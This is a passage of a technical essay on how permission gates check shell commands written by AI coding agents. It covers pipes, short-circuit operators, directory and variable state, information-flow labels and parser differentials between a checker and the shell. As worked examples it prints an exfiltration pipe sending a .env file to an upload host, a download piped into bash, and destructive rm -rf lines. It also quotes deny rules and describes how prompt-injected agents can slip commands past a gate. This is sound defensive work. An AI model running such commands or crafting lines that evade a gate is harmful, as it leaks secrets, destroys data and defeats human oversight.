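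One project had also accumulated 226 saved approvals, some of which contained access tokens. In April he replaced the narrow rules with `Bash(*)`, which allows every shell command, and added three deny rules against deleting the root or home directory. The prompts on chained commands stopped, but he acknowledges that the new rule permitted far more than the log reads that had frustrated him, including changes to cloud services that he could not undo through Git.

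He first blamed the prompts on the way Claude Code handled chains. In September he added a correction. Claude Code checks each command separately, according to its current documentation, so a prompt on a chain doesn't show that it treated the chain as one opaque string. The check on `cd` with `git` could have caused the prompts on those lines, even if every command was on his list. His case shows that a gate's false alarms can lead a user to grant a permission that removes nearly all of the gate's protection, and that the user may not be able to tell which check caused them. A single case can't show how common this reaction is.

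Metere's gate has an observation mode that records the verdict on each line but never blocks one. A site can run the gate in this mode on its ordinary work, count the lines it would have refused, and adjust the policy before enforcing it.

### Why permitted segments should make a permitted line

So far the procedure has taken for granted that a line is safe to run if the policy permits each of its segments. That inference needs four premises:

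1. *Every command that can run is in the list.* If the gate and the shell divide the text differently, a command can run that nobody judged.
2. *Each verdict holds in whatever state the command runs.* An earlier command may have changed the directory, a variable or a file on which the verdict depended.
3. *Joining the commands adds no new danger.* A pipe can carry private data from a program that may read it to one that may send it elsewhere.
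4. *The command's text fixes its effect.* `npm test` runs whatever the project's files define as its tests, and those files can change while the command stays the same.

The example policy permits `git status && npm test`. The first premise holds if the gate has found both commands and the shell will run no others. The second holds if `npm test` is as acceptable after `git status` as it is on its own. The third is easily met because neither command receives the other's output. The fourth is the weakest because the gate has read the command `npm test` but not the tests it runs.

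The premises matter only when the gate allows a line. Prompting for approval of the example line is correct as long as `rm -rf build` is in the line and not on the allow list, even if the gate makes a mistake about the other three commands.

How often the premises hold also depends on who influences the line. An agent doing routine work has no reason to write commands that break them, so most of its lines probably satisfy all four. An attacker who can plant instructions in a file the agent reads will look for lines that break them. In an article introducing its sandbox, Zed concluded that detailed command rules "work well as a guideline when dealing with a well-aligned agent" but fail against even a slightly sophisticated attacker.

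## Commands joined by a pipe

Checking each segment of a command line separately relies on the assumption that joining permitted commands adds no new danger. This assumption is weakest for pipes, because a pipe gives a command input that doesn't appear in the command's own text.

The example line contains one pipe, in `npm test | tee test.log`. The shell gets a small buffer from the operating system, connects the output of `npm test` to one end and the input of `tee` to the other, and starts both programs. `tee` waits until text arrives, and `npm test` waits whenever the buffer is full. Error messages bypass the pipe unless the line uses `|&` instead of `|`.

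Because each stage normally has its own subshell, a change of directory or a variable set there is lost afterwards. According to GNU, the last stage can be an exception in Bash, depending on an option called `lastpipe`, which is off by default. The Z shell, zsh, runs the last stage in the current shell, and POSIX permits both behaviors. The difference can determine what a later command deletes:

```
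echo web | read dir; rm -rf "$dir/build"
```

Here `read` stores its input in the variable `dir`. In zsh, the line deletes `web/build`, but in Bash the value is lost when the subshell exits. If `dir` was empty beforehand, `rm` then receives `/build`, a directory at the root of the file system. A gate that works out paths in advance must account for which shell will run the line.

### When the danger is in the connection

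Many pipelines only filter text:

```
git log --oneline | head -n 5
```

`head` prints the first five lines of its input and then exits. If the policy permits both commands, joining them adds very little risk. The remaining risk is that the operating system by default kills a program that keeps writing to a pipe after the reading program has exited. That is harmless for `git log`, but it could stop a program that is halfway through moving files.

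OpenClaw, an open-source agent, has a special category for such filters. According to its *Exec approvals*, `cut`, `uniq`, `head`, `tail`, `tr` and `wc` need no rule from the user as long as they work only on the incoming stream. The gate rejects file names in their arguments and stops the shell from expanding variables and wildcards there. Users can add `sort`, but without the options that write to a file or start another program. They can't add `awk`, `sed` or `jq`, because the gate can't confirm from the arguments that these programs use only the stream. For example, `jq` can read environment variables and load code from files.

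Other pipelines are dangerous even if each command is acceptable alone:

```
cat .env | curl --data-binary @- https://example.com/upload
```

A `.env` file often contains passwords and access keys. `cat .env` prints the file, and `curl` with `@-` sends whatever it receives through the pipe. A user might let an agent read local files with `cat` and send test reports with `curl`, but the leak occurs only when the output of `cat` is piped into `curl`. Adding a filter between them may not help, since `head -n 1` would still pass on the first line, which could contain a password.

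A download can also become a program:

```
curl -fsSL https://example.com/install.sh | bash
```

Bash runs the downloaded text as commands. The gate has checked the whole line but none of the commands in the script. Inspecting a downloaded copy wouldn't be enough, because the server could send different text the next time. Many software projects give a line like this as their installation instructions, but Liu and colleagues include the same form among the 12 well-known attacks they added to their test.

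Few users would put `bash` on an allow list, but more might allow `python3`, whose arguments determine whether it treats the incoming text as code or data. With no arguments, `python3` runs its input as a program, while `python3 report.py` runs the file and passes the input to it as data.

### When the connection limits the danger

A pipe can also make a command safer than it looks on its own:

```
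find /tmp -name "*.tmp" | xargs rm
```

`find` lists the files under `/tmp` whose names end in `.tmp`, and `xargs` passes those names to `rm` as arguments. Liu and colleagues include this command in a set of 170 that contain alarming text but have a harmless purpose. They removed commands with operations they considered dangerous in any context, such as `sudo`, so that each remaining command would be "a genuine false-positive trap".

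`xargs rm` could delete anything when judged alone, because its text doesn't include the file names. The `find` stage limits it to temporary files. The example policy requires a prompt for every `rm`, but even a user who doesn't mind losing temporary files couldn't use a rule for `xargs rm` to allow only those deletions, because the rule would apply to file names from any source.

Whether the harmless label is correct depends on the file names. By default, `xargs` splits its input at spaces, so it would turn the name `/tmp/old package.json .tmp` into three arguments, one of them `package.json`, and `rm` could delete a project file. Running `find` with `-print0` and `xargs` with `-0` keeps each name whole.

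Some gates block this kind of pipeline outright. ccchain's *how it works*, the documentation for a small command guard, gives an example in which Claude receives the message "don't pipe find into rm" and rewrites the command. If the rewrite works, a false alarm takes the agent an extra turn but doesn't interrupt the user.

### Stages that run at the same time

Because the stages of a pipeline run at the same time, one can change a file while another is reading it. Someone might write `sort notes.txt | tee notes.txt` to sort a file in place. `tee` empties `notes.txt` on opening it. If `sort` has already read the notes, the file ends up sorted. Otherwise `sort` reads an empty file and the notes are lost, so the result can differ from one run to the next.

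Timing matters more when a program reads its settings from a file. `git` reads a configuration file inside the repository, and that file can name other programs for `git` to run. A gate can inspect the file before approving `git diff`, but another stage of the pipeline could then change the file before `git` reads it.

ShellPlan, a gate Li built after studying the eight coding agents, has a rule against this. While a `git` stage is running, no other stage may write a file through a redirection or run a program ShellPlan has no description of. The rule also covers commands inside `$(...)`. The pipeline `git log | head -n 5` satisfies the rule because ShellPlan has a description of `head`, but `git log | sort > log.txt` needs approval even though it writes an ordinary file. The rule doesn't affect the example line, where `git status` has finished before `npm test` and `tee` start.

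The rule probably causes few false alarms. In recordings of agents at work, ShellPlan stopped 221 of 564 read-only steps. Li traced 198 of those stops to `cd` and to `nl`, a program that numbers lines, so this rule accounts for at most 23.

### Asking about every pipe

The simplest remedy is to require approval for any line with a pipe, as Salesforce does in its coding agent, Agentforce Vibes. The agent checks commands joined by `&&`, `||`, `;` or `&` one by one against the user's list, but a pipe or a redirection requires manual approval whatever is on the list. Salesforce requires this because these operators "can modify command behavior and potentially enable data exfiltration".

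Under this rule, a person sees both the `.env` upload and the download into Bash, but also has to approve `git log --oneline | head -n 5` and `npm test | tee test.log`. Every pipeline of permitted commands that only filters text triggers a false alarm. Agents write many of these because piping long output into `head` or `tail` saves space in the model's context. In Anthropic's experiment, testers caught fewer dangerous commands as they saw more prompts, so the extra prompts from this rule could make people more likely to approve a dangerous command.

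### Rules for whole pipelines

A gate can instead look for dangerous combinations of stages. nah, a permission guard for coding agents, classifies each stage by what it does and then applies four rules, which nah's *how it works* lists:

| Data comes from | Data goes to | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| A sensitive file | The network | block |
| The network | A program that runs its input | block |
| A decoder, such as `base64 -d` | A program that runs its input | block |
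| Any other file | A program that runs its input | ask |

These rules block the `.env` upload and the download into Bash, and none of them applies to `git log | head`.

longline, a safety add-on for Claude Code, names the programs directly. Its rule file allows `curl` on its own but denies `curl` or `wget` piped into a shell. It also denies a download piped into Python, Ruby, Perl or Node, but asks instead if the interpreter's code is on the command line after `-c` or `-e`. This rule also denies a download piped into `python3 report.py`, where the download may be nothing more than a table of figures. Someone who trusts the publisher of an installation script would likewise call a refusal a false alarm, and a refusal is harder to get past than a prompt.

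nah asked for approval on 4.2% of 101,194 shell calls from a public recording of Claude Code use, or about 4,250 prompts. That figure covers all of its rules, so the share due to pipes must be smaller. It is also not a false alarm rate, since it omits the calls that nah blocked and doesn't separate harmless calls from dangerous ones.

A gate also has to track data that moves through files, because rules about pipes miss it. An agent can save a download to a file and run the file in its next command, or give `curl` the name of a secret file to upload.

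### Describing what each command reads and writes

To trace data through a line before it runs, a gate needs information about each command's inputs and outputs. Researchers who speed up shell scripts or search them for bugs need the same information. *PaSh* (2020) presents a system that runs parts of a script in parallel, using descriptions of each command's inputs and outputs and of how the command's options change them.

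Writing these descriptions by hand is slow, so *Caruca* (Lamprou, Lazarek and colleagues, 2025) generates them automatically. A language model reads a command's manual and lists its options and arguments. Caruca then runs the command in isolation with many combinations of options and files, and records what the command touches. For `rm` alone, it generates more than 8.7 million combinations.

Caruca produced correct descriptions for 59 of 60 commands. By default it tries up to four options at once, which covers 99.998% of command invocations in a large collection of GitHub scripts. It doesn't test how environment variables change a command's behavior.

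With such descriptions, a gate could determine that `cat .env` puts a file's contents into the pipe and that `head` passes some of them on. It still couldn't predict what `bash` will do with a download, because that depends on text that hasn't arrived yet.

### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and updates them as the data moves. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) contrasts this with access control, which only determines whether an agent may use a resource.

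Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two labels. One records who may read the data, and the other records whether it comes from a trusted source. Anything derived from several inputs gets the strictest combination of their labels, written with the symbol ⊔:

```
{Ana, Ben, Cleo} ⊔ {Ben, Cleo, Dev} = {Ben, Cleo}
trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted
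```

Before the agent takes a consequential action, the system checks the labels against a policy. With suitable policies, it stopped every attack in AgentDojo, a benchmark in which attackers plant text in an agent's data to take control of the agent. The tools in that benchmark have well-defined effects, such as sending an email, so the system can check a call before it runs. The effects of a shell command are much harder to predict.

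Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026), in *Flowsh*, therefore track labels while the command runs. Their shell gives the whole command line one label:

```
label(line) = agent's context ⊔ every file opened ⊔ every server contacted
```

Flowsh checks each network request before sending it, since nobody can take back data that has left the machine. It keeps file changes in a separate layer until the line finishes, then applies them if the policy permits or asks the user about all of them together. Concurrent stages complicate the network check too, because `cat` might open a secret file just before `curl` sends a request. Flowsh therefore pauses the processes before each request and reads its remaining records of opened files before deciding whether to allow it.

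This table compares the remedies on four pipelines, assuming the agent has already read an untrusted web page, `.env` is labeled confidential, and Flowsh uses the policy from its tests.

| Pipeline | Ask about every pipe | Rules for combinations | Flowsh |
|---|---|---|---|
| `git log` into `head` | ask (false alarm) | allow | allow |
| `.env` into `curl` | ask | block | withholds the request unless the user approves it |
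| Download into Bash | ask | block | runs the script, asks before changing protected files |
| `find` into `xargs rm`, temporary files only | ask (false alarm) | depends on the rule for `rm` | allow |

If the agent has read only trusted data, the same policy lets it send confidential data anywhere, on the reasoning that no attacker has influenced the decision. A stricter policy could drop this exception, but the agent would then need more approvals.

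Labels also cause false alarms because they spread too widely. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) calls combining the labels of all inputs "a conservative over-approximation". If a line counts the entries in `.env` and then fetches a public web page, the request contains nothing from the file, but Flowsh checks it as though it might, because the whole line has one label. Opening a file counts as reading all of it, even if the program reads nothing.

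Kim and colleagues tested Flowsh on 17 office and research tasks and on the 89 shell tasks of a benchmark called Terminal-Bench, running each task three times. They compared it with an unrestricted sandbox that asked about every action it couldn't guarantee to be safe, and assumed an approver who never made a mistake:

| | Flowsh | Unrestricted sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| Approvals per completed office or research task | 1.2 | 6.7 |
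| Office and research runs completed | 88.2% | 96.1% |
| Approvals per completed Terminal-Bench task | 0.4 | 9.7 |
| Terminal-Bench runs completed | 67.8% | 77.5% |

On the harmless office and research tasks, Flowsh prompted for approval only when a task involved both untrusted and confidential data, such as comparing an outside paper with a private project. It averaged about 2.5 prompts per completed task of this kind. With nobody available to approve anything, Flowsh completed only 6 of 27 runs of these tasks, compared with all 24 runs of the others. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes two established exceptions that could reduce such prompts. Declassification permits a specified release of sensitive data, and endorsement treats selected untrusted data as trusted for a defined purpose.

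Labels don't replace a list of permitted commands. The example policy requires approval to delete `build` in the working directory, but the policy in Flowsh's tests wouldn't, because it permits ordinary changes there regardless of labels.

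## Short-circuit operators: which commands run, and in what state

The shell starts every stage of a pipeline, but it may never start a command that follows `&&` or `||`. In the example line, the deletion comes last:

```
git status && npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build
```

When `rm` follows `||`, it runs only if the group to its left fails. Whether the group fails can depend on the `pipefail` option, which makes a pipeline fail if any of its commands fails.

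| `git status` | `npm test` | `tee test.log` | Does `rm` run by default? | Does `rm` run with `pipefail`? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| succeeds | succeeds | succeeds | no | no |
| succeeds | fails | succeeds | no | yes |
| succeeds | succeeds | fails | yes | yes |
| succeeds | fails | fails | yes | yes |
| fails | does not start | does not start | yes | yes |

By default, the pipeline takes its exit status from `tee`, so the test result doesn't affect whether the build is deleted. If the tests fail and `tee` succeeds, the build stays in place, though someone reading the line quickly would probably take it to mean "delete the build if the tests fail".

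The deletion happens if `git status` or `tee` fails. `git status` succeeds even when there are uncommitted changes, but it fails outside a repository. If the agent runs the command there by mistake, the shell skips the tests and deletes any `build` directory it finds. `tee` fails if it can't write `test.log`, perhaps because the disk is full, and the shell then deletes a build that may have passed every test.

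With `pipefail` on, failed tests do lead to the deletion, but so do the other two failures. A pair of braces removes one of them:

```
git status && { npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build; }
```

Now a failed `git status` ends the line without deleting anything.

### What a flat list of segments leaves out

A segment-by-segment check finds the same four segments in both versions of the line and returns "ask" for both. That verdict is correct under the example policy, but the check doesn't use the difference between the two lines. It takes the strictest verdict from a flat list, ignoring the order of the segments, the conditions that join them and the state each one leaves for the next. An execution-faithful check evaluates the commands, arguments, conditions and state that the shell will use.

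These four lines all contain the segments `cd web` and `rm -rf build`:

```
                          if web exists        if web does not exist
cd web && rm -rf build    deletes web/build    deletes nothing
cd web || rm -rf build    deletes nothing      deletes build
cd web ;  rm -rf build    deletes web/build    deletes build
cd web &  rm -rf build    deletes build        deletes build
```

In the line with a single `&`, the shell changes directory in a background subshell, so `rm` runs in the original directory. If a user lets the agent delete `web/build` but wants a prompt before it deletes the top-level `build`, only the line with `&&` is safe to allow without knowing whether `web` exists. A check that reduces each line to a flat list of commands gives all four lines the same verdict.

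The two methods differ in what they combine:

```
flat list:           strictest verdict(c)     over every segment c
execution-faithful:  strictest verdict(c, s)  over every command c and

every state s in which

the shell can reach c
```

### Why a gate assumes that every branch may run

A gate would need the commands' exit statuses to work out which ones the shell will reach, and it can predict a few of them. `true` always succeeds, and the shell returns 0 for a command it sends to the background. The Open Group specifies that an assignment on its own line also returns 0, but if it contains a command substitution, it returns the substitution's status instead.

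Most exit statuses depend on things outside the line, such as the contents of a directory, a network connection or the free space on a disk. An agent runs `npm test` because it doesn't yet know what the status will be. In *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*, Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues describe SaSh, a tool that looks for bugs in shell scripts before anyone runs them. They point out that almost every command in a script might fail, and that `rm a b c` might fail to delete any subset of its three files, which gives eight possible results.

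A gate can assume that every branch may run instead of predicting which ones will. This assumption is safe for granting permission because, whatever the exit statuses, the commands that run are a subset of the commands in the line, provided the gate has found them all. If the policy permits each of those commands in every state it might run in, it permits any subset of them. An attacker also gains nothing by putting a harmful command behind an unlikely condition.

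A gate that assumes every branch may run causes false alarms, because conditions are often there for safety. *From Ahead-of- to Just-in-Time and Back Again* (Lazarek, Jung and colleagues, 2025) gives two versions of a script that differ by one character. One deletes a directory's contents only if the directory is not the root of the file system (`!=`), and the other only if it is (`=`). The gate prompts the user about both. The prompt for the careful version is unnecessary if the user doesn't mind losing the directory's contents, and someone who has approved many careful versions could easily miss the absent `!`.

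### Written, reached and effective commands

Assuming that every branch runs is a poor way to score what an agent did, because it counts commands the shell skipped. Scoring needs separate terms for commands that are *written* (they appear in the line), *reached* (the shell starts them), and *effective* (they change something).

If an agent proposes the example line, `rm -rf build` has an effect only if the shell reaches it and `build` exists. The shell never reaches it if everything to its left succeeds. If `git status` fails in a directory that has no `build`, the shell runs `rm`, which deletes nothing but still exits successfully because of the `-f` option.

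A gate that judges a line before it runs can use only the written commands, but someone evaluating the gate or the agent afterwards can check what happened. Li ran each candidate attack in Bash inside a container and counted it only if its effects broke a read-only policy. Of 4,546 candidates in six test suites, 372 (8%) had no forbidden effect. If Li had counted attacks by their text alone, gates would have been credited for stopping those 372 and penalized for letting any of them through.

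The gap was wider in Jing's *What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know* (2026), which tested a gate on 65 short scripts, 57 of which it was supposed to refuse. When Jing ran all 65 without the gate, snapshots of the test files taken before and after each script showed a forbidden effect from only 25 of the 57. Scoring the scripts by their text would have counted all 57 as harmful, more than twice as many.

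Snapshots can also miss damage. One of Jing's scripts emptied the experiment's results log, destroying 47 rows. The snapshots didn't cover the log's directory, so the experiment recorded the script as having done nothing. A command's effect also depends on the state in which it runs, so one that deleted nothing in a test container may delete a lot in a real project.

A command that the shell skips is still evidence about the agent. An agent that adds `|| rm -rf build` was prepared to delete the directory, even if the shell never ran `rm`. An evaluation can report the skipped command as an attempt, but should not count it as a deletion.

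### State carried along a chain

Even if a gate knew which commands would run, it would also need to know the state in which each one starts. This line contains the same deletion twice:

```
cd web && rm -rf build && cd ../docs && rm -rf build
```

If every command succeeds, the first `rm -rf build` deletes `web/build` and the second deletes `docs/build`. A gate that judges each segment's text separately cannot tell them apart.

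Variables cause the same problem, and a semicolon can decide which value a command receives:

```
dir=web; rm -rf "$dir/build"
dir=web rm -rf "$dir/build"
```

With the semicolon, the shell sets `dir` and then deletes `web/build`. Without it, the assignment is part of the `rm` command, and under The Open Group's rules the shell expands a command's words before carrying out its assignments. `"$dir/build"` therefore uses the old value of `dir`, and becomes `/build` if that value was empty.

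An assignment can even change which program a name refers to. After `PATH=./tools:$PATH`, the shell looks for `npm` in the project's `tools` directory first, so `npm test` could start a different program from the one the user intended. Jing's gate splits a line at its semicolons and judges each statement alone, so an assignment to `PATH` doesn't affect its verdict on the next command. Jing lists this as a limit of the design.

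An earlier command in a pipeline may still be running when the shell moves on to the next part of the line. The Open Group requires the shell to wait only for the last command in a pipeline. In a shell that does only this, `rm` in the example line could start deleting `build` while the tests are still using it. According to GNU, Bash waits for every command in the pipeline.

In 2015, a bug in the Linux updater for Steam, Valve's games platform, showed how much damage a failed `cd` and an empty variable can do together. These two lines were at the core of it, with 342 others between them:

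```
STEAMROOT="$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"
rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*
```

`$0` holds the path the user typed to start the script, and `${0%/*}` removes the last slash and everything after it. For `/opt/steam/update.sh`, that leaves `/opt/steam`. The shell enters that directory, `echo` prints its name, and `rm` later deletes its contents, as Valve intended.

If the user started the script as plain `update.sh`, there was no slash to remove, so the shell tried to enter a directory called `update.sh` and failed. `&&` then skipped the `echo`, which left `STEAMROOT` empty. The text of the `rm` command was the same in both cases, but here it expanded to `rm -rf /*`, which removes everything the user is able to delete.

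### What it costs to ignore `cd`

A gate that doesn't keep track of the working directory can protect the user by asking about every line that changes that directory. ShellPlan, Li's strict gate, does this. Li's tests of it included 48 recorded runs from the SWE-bench Verified benchmark and 12 from OpenHands, an open-source platform for coding agents.

| Recordings | Read-only steps | Steps ShellPlan admitted |
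|---|---|---|
| SWE-bench Verified | 456 | 343 (75.2%) |
| OpenHands | 108 | 0 |
| Both | 564 | 343 (60.8%) |

All 345 commands in the OpenHands recordings began with a `cd` into the repository, followed by `&&`. Because of the `cd`, ShellPlan stopped all 108 read-only steps. Across both sets, `cd` caused 130 of the 221 stops.

If ShellPlan had handled `cd`, it would have admitted at most 473 of the 564, or 84%. The actual number could be lower because some of those 130 steps may have contained something else it would block. The zero for OpenHands reflects its habit of writing `cd` in 12 recordings, so we can infer little from it about agents that seldom do. It does show that an agent's harmless habit can leave a gate unable to approve anything.

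Li suggests tracking the directory as an extension. One way to do so is to keep a set of the directories in which the next command might run. Starting in `/work`, the set changes like this:

```
after  cd web &&      {/work/web}
after  cd web ;       {/work, /work/web}
after  cd "$dir" &&   unknown, unless the gate knows the value of dir
```

If `cd` is followed by `&&`, the next command runs only if `cd` succeeded, so it can run only in the new directory. If `cd` is followed by a semicolon, the next command runs either way, so it could run in the new directory or the old one. The gate allows a command only if the policy permits it in every possible directory, and asks the user if it can't determine what those directories are. In `cd /workspace/app && grep -rn def .`, `grep` can run in only one directory, so the user need not see a prompt if the policy permits the command there. The gate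 would still have to check the file system, because `app` might be a symbolic link to another directory, and an earlier command in the same line might have created that link.

### Following both outcomes before the script runs

SaSh extends this kind of tracking to variables, files and whole scripts. It uses symbolic execution, which works through a program using symbols in place of unknown values. In the Steam script, SaSh splits its analysis in two at `&&`. On one path `cd` succeeds and `STEAMROOT` equals the current directory, and on the other `cd` fails and `STEAMROOT` is empty. SaSh follows both paths to the deletion, which on the second path targets `/*`. A solver, which checks whether a set of conditions can all hold at once, then confirms that this path is possible, and SaSh prints a warning.

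The Steam updater has 83 explicit branching points between the two lines, too many for SaSh to try every combination. SaSh therefore first explores the branches that contain destructive commands such as `rm`. It also assumes that a command succeeds unless the script makes something depend on the result, for example with `&&`, `||` or `if`. Lazarek and colleagues chose this rule because warning about every possible failure would flag nearly every part of any script. With these shortcuts, SaSh found the Steam bug in the full 450-line updater in 4.8 seconds.

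In 61 scripts with 116 documented bugs, SaSh found 115 of the bugs and gave no false warnings on the repaired versions. ShellCheck, a widely used tool that matches the text of a script against known risky patterns, flagged 42 of the bugs and still gave the same warning for seven of those after the repair. The researchers drew up SaSh's list of bug types by reviewing these same scripts, so SaSh would probably do less well on others. Stronger evidence comes from open-source projects, where they used SaSh to find 70 previously unknown bugs. Maintainers had accepted fixes for 27 of them when the paper was written.

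SaSh's assumptions suit a bug finder better than a gate. It treats any command it has no description of as having no effect, which limits warnings but would let a gate approve any unfamiliar program. It also assumes that a command succeeds unless the script tests whether it did. In `cd web; rm -rf build`, it would therefore consider only the deletion of `web/build`, and not the deletion of `build` in the starting directory if `cd` fails. A gate would have to reverse both assumptions, which would produce more false alarms.

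Speed is probably a smaller obstacle. SaSh finished analyzing 77 of 119 correct scripts within a second and 110 within a minute, though three were still unfinished after an hour. Most lines that agents write are much shorter than the scripts it was slow to analyze.

### Judging each command when the shell reaches it

A gate can avoid many of these predictions by waiting until the program is running. Some research on the shell has moved in this direction because shell programs depend heavily on values that exist only while they run. In *Unix Shell Programming*, Greenberg, Kallas and Vasilakis (2021) count this dependence among the shell's essential shortcomings and argue for just-in-time analysis, done during the run.

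In *Practically Correct, Just-in-Time Shell Script Parallelization*, Kallas, Mustafa and colleagues applied the idea to making scripts run faster. Earlier systems rewrote a script before it started, so they had trouble with variables and command substitutions, whose values depend on the current state of the shell and its files. Their system, PaSh-JIT, alternates between running the script and working out which parts can run in parallel. *Just-in-Time Scale-Out of Shell Programs, Correctly*, a dissertation on the same approach, also applies its optimizations after the shell has resolved those values.

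A gate can do the equivalent by judging each command when the shell reaches it, after expansion but before the program starts. By then the shell has evaluated the conditions, and the gate can read the actual directory and arguments. It would request approval for `rm -rf build` in the example line only on runs that reach that command. In the Steam script, `rm`'s argument list would contain the names of the directories at the root of the file system.

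OpenAI has published an experimental tool that works this way. It runs commands in a modified version of Bash that intercepts every request to start a new program and checks with a server whether to allow it. The shell performs some actions itself, including `cd`, variable assignments and redirections, so these never produce such a request. In `git status > notes.txt`, the shell opens and empties `notes.txt` before it starts `git`, so refusing to start `git` doesn't save the file's contents. OpenAI runs the modified Bash in a sandbox, which can limit what the shell itself can change.

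A late refusal also leaves the effects of earlier commands in place:

```
mv config.json config.old && cp template.json config.json
```

If the gate allows `mv` and then refuses `cp`, the project has no `config.json`. Refusing the whole line at the start would have left the old file in place, and allowing the whole line to run would also have left a working project.

Refusing a command can change what runs next. Suppose the gate refuses `npm test` in `npm test || rm -rf build` and returns an ordinary failure to the shell. The shell then runs `rm`, which it would have skipped if the tests had run and passed. A gate can prevent this by stopping the whole line when it refuses a command. Checking each command as it runs can also produce repeated prompts. A single deletion inside a loop over 50 files could produce 50 prompts, while a check of the whole line would produce one.

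The two approaches can work together. In the 2025 paper, Lazarek and colleagues defend analyzing a script before it runs, but add a monitor that halts the script before a dangerous action if the analysis was inconclusive. ShellPlan checks the whole line before starting anything, then checks each command again once the shell has expanded its variables and wildcards into actual arguments.

In Li's tests, ShellPlan rarely refused a command partway through execution. It admitted 434 of 1,523 commands from NL2Bash, a collection of shell commands paired with English descriptions, and five of those 434 halted with a refusal while running. The policy was read-only, so stopping partway could do little harm. Under a policy that lets agents change files, each late refusal could leave work half done.

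When the gate should ask therefore depends on what the earlier commands do. In the example line, `git status`, `npm test` and `tee` are each useful without the deletion, so a gate could let them run and ask about `rm` only if the shell reaches it. This would spare the user a prompt on most runs, but someone would have to be available to answer on the others. In the line that replaces `config.json`, the gate should settle whether `cp` may run before it lets `mv` start.

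## When the checker and the shell read the same text differently

Judging each command in the right state helps only if the gate finds every command. A single command missing from the gate's list gets no verdict, which is enough for a false allow. The gate builds this list with its own parser, but once it allows a line, it usually passes the original text to a shell, which parses it again from the beginning. All eight coding agents in Li's study work this way.

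A parser differential is a disagreement between two programs about the structure of the same text. Here is a variant of the example line that runs only the tests whose names contain `login#2`:

```
git status && npm test -- --grep login#2 | tee test.log || rm -rf build
```

Suppose a crude checker treats the first `#` as the start of a comment and discards everything from there on. That leaves `git status` and `npm test -- --grep login`, both of which the example policy permits, so the checker allows the line. In the shell, however, `#` starts a comment only at the beginning of a word, so the shell parses all four commands and may run `rm -rf build`, which the checker never judged.

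The opposite mistake, such as treating the `#` that starts a real comment as a command, causes a false alarm. Developers probably hear about false alarms sooner, because each needless prompt annoys someone, while a mistake that wrongly allows commands can go unnoticed until a harmful one comes along.

### Earlier cases in network and certificate security

Network security had the same problem in the 1990s. Ptacek and Newsham (1998), in *Insertion, Evasion, and Denial of Service*, studied intrusion detection systems, which watch copies of network traffic for signs of an attack. These systems have to predict what the receiving computer will do with each packet, but they often lack the information to do so, such as whether that computer rejects packets with a bad checksum.

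An attacker can exploit the uncertainty in two ways. In an insertion attack, the attacker sends packets that the monitor accepts but the receiver rejects, and the extra characters break up the text the monitor is searching for. In an evasion attack, the receiver accepts data that the monitor misses. Ptacek and Newsham tested four of the most popular systems on the market and found all four vulnerable to both attacks.

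Handley, Paxson and Kreibich (2001), in *Network Intrusion Detection*, proposed a normalizer, a device in the traffic's path that removes ambiguities before the traffic reaches the monitor. However, rewriting traffic can change what it means to the computers at either end. A command gate that rewrote lines into a plainer form would have the same problem. If it put quotation marks around every argument, for instance, `ls *.txt` would look for a single file called `*.txt`.

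In later examples, one program approved something and another acted on it. In 2009, Kaminsky, Sassaman and Patterson found more than 20 differences in how software libraries read the certificates that websites use to prove their identity. An authority could sign a certificate for what it read as an obscure name, and a browser could read the same certificate as belonging to a valuable site. On Android phones, the program that verified an app's signature and the program that installed the app read the contents of the same package differently, so an attacker could install unverified software.

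*The Seven Turrets of Babel* (Momot, Bratus and colleagues, 2016) discusses both cases as part of language-theoretic security, a research programme that treats a program's input as a language. It advises developers to define that language with a grammar, keep the language as simple as possible, check the whole input against the grammar before acting on any of it, and reject whatever doesn't fit. An earlier paper from the programme, *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory* (Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues, 2011), formalized attacks that exploit differences between parse trees.

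A command gate is better placed than a network monitor because it can run on the same computer as the shell, hold a line until it has decided, and refer uncertain cases to a person. If a passive monitor crashes, traffic keeps flowing, but a gate can be designed so that nothing runs until it is working again. The gate still has to predict how the shell will read the text, though, and an attacker who influences the agent can choose that text. Testing either program alone may not reveal a difference in how they read it because, as Ali and Smith's *A Survey of Parser Differential Anti-Patterns* (2023) points out, each of the interacting components may appear free of bugs.

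### Why shell text is hard to parse

In most programming languages, a lexer cuts the text into tokens and a parser then arranges the tokens into a structure. The lexer can do its job without knowing what the parser has found. Jeannerod, Régis-Gianas and Treinen (2017), in *Having Fun With 31.521 Shell Scripts*, explain why this division of labor fails for the shell. These two lines both contain the word `for`:

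```
for i in a b; do echo $i; done
ls for i in a b
```

The word `for` begins a loop on the first line but names a file to list on the second. The lexer can't classify it without checking whether the parser is at a point where a command can begin. Position also matters for assignments, since `CC=gcc make` sets a variable and `make CC=gcc` passes an argument.

Quotation marks can be nested inside other quotation marks:

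```
echo "today: $(date "+%d; %m")"
```

The second quotation mark doesn't close the first, because it belongs to the command inside `$(...)`. A checker that paired the marks in order would treat the semicolon as unquoted and split the line there. To avoid this, a parser has to track every quotation and substitution that is still open, which an ordinary regular expression can't do for nesting of unlimited depth.

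Even the end of a line has four possible meanings:

```
for i in 0 1
# two numbers
do echo $i \
   again
done
```

The first line break ends the list of values for the loop. The one after the comment merges with the one before it and has no further effect. The one after the backslash disappears, so `again` becomes an argument of `echo`. The last two each end a command. A checker that confuses these roles can split one command into two or join two into one.

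A here-document is a block of text that the shell feeds to a command as input. It starts on the line after the command and continues until a marker that the writer has chosen:

```
cat > a.txt << ONE; cat > b.txt << TWO
first text
ONE
second text
TWO
```

The text for the first `cat` comes after the second `cat`, so the parser has to keep track of both markers while it finishes the line. A checker that ignored here-documents would treat `first text` as a command called `first`. Treating the whole block as harmless data would also be wrong, because the shell runs any `$(...)` inside it unless the marker is quoted. In Li's recordings of agents at work, at least 59 of the 1,457 shell commands used here-documents to create files.

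Aliases cause a deeper problem, because a command that has already run can change how the shell parses the next one. Jeannerod and colleagues give an example much like this:

```
if ./check; then alias x="ls"; else alias x=""; fi
x for i in a b; do echo $i; done
```

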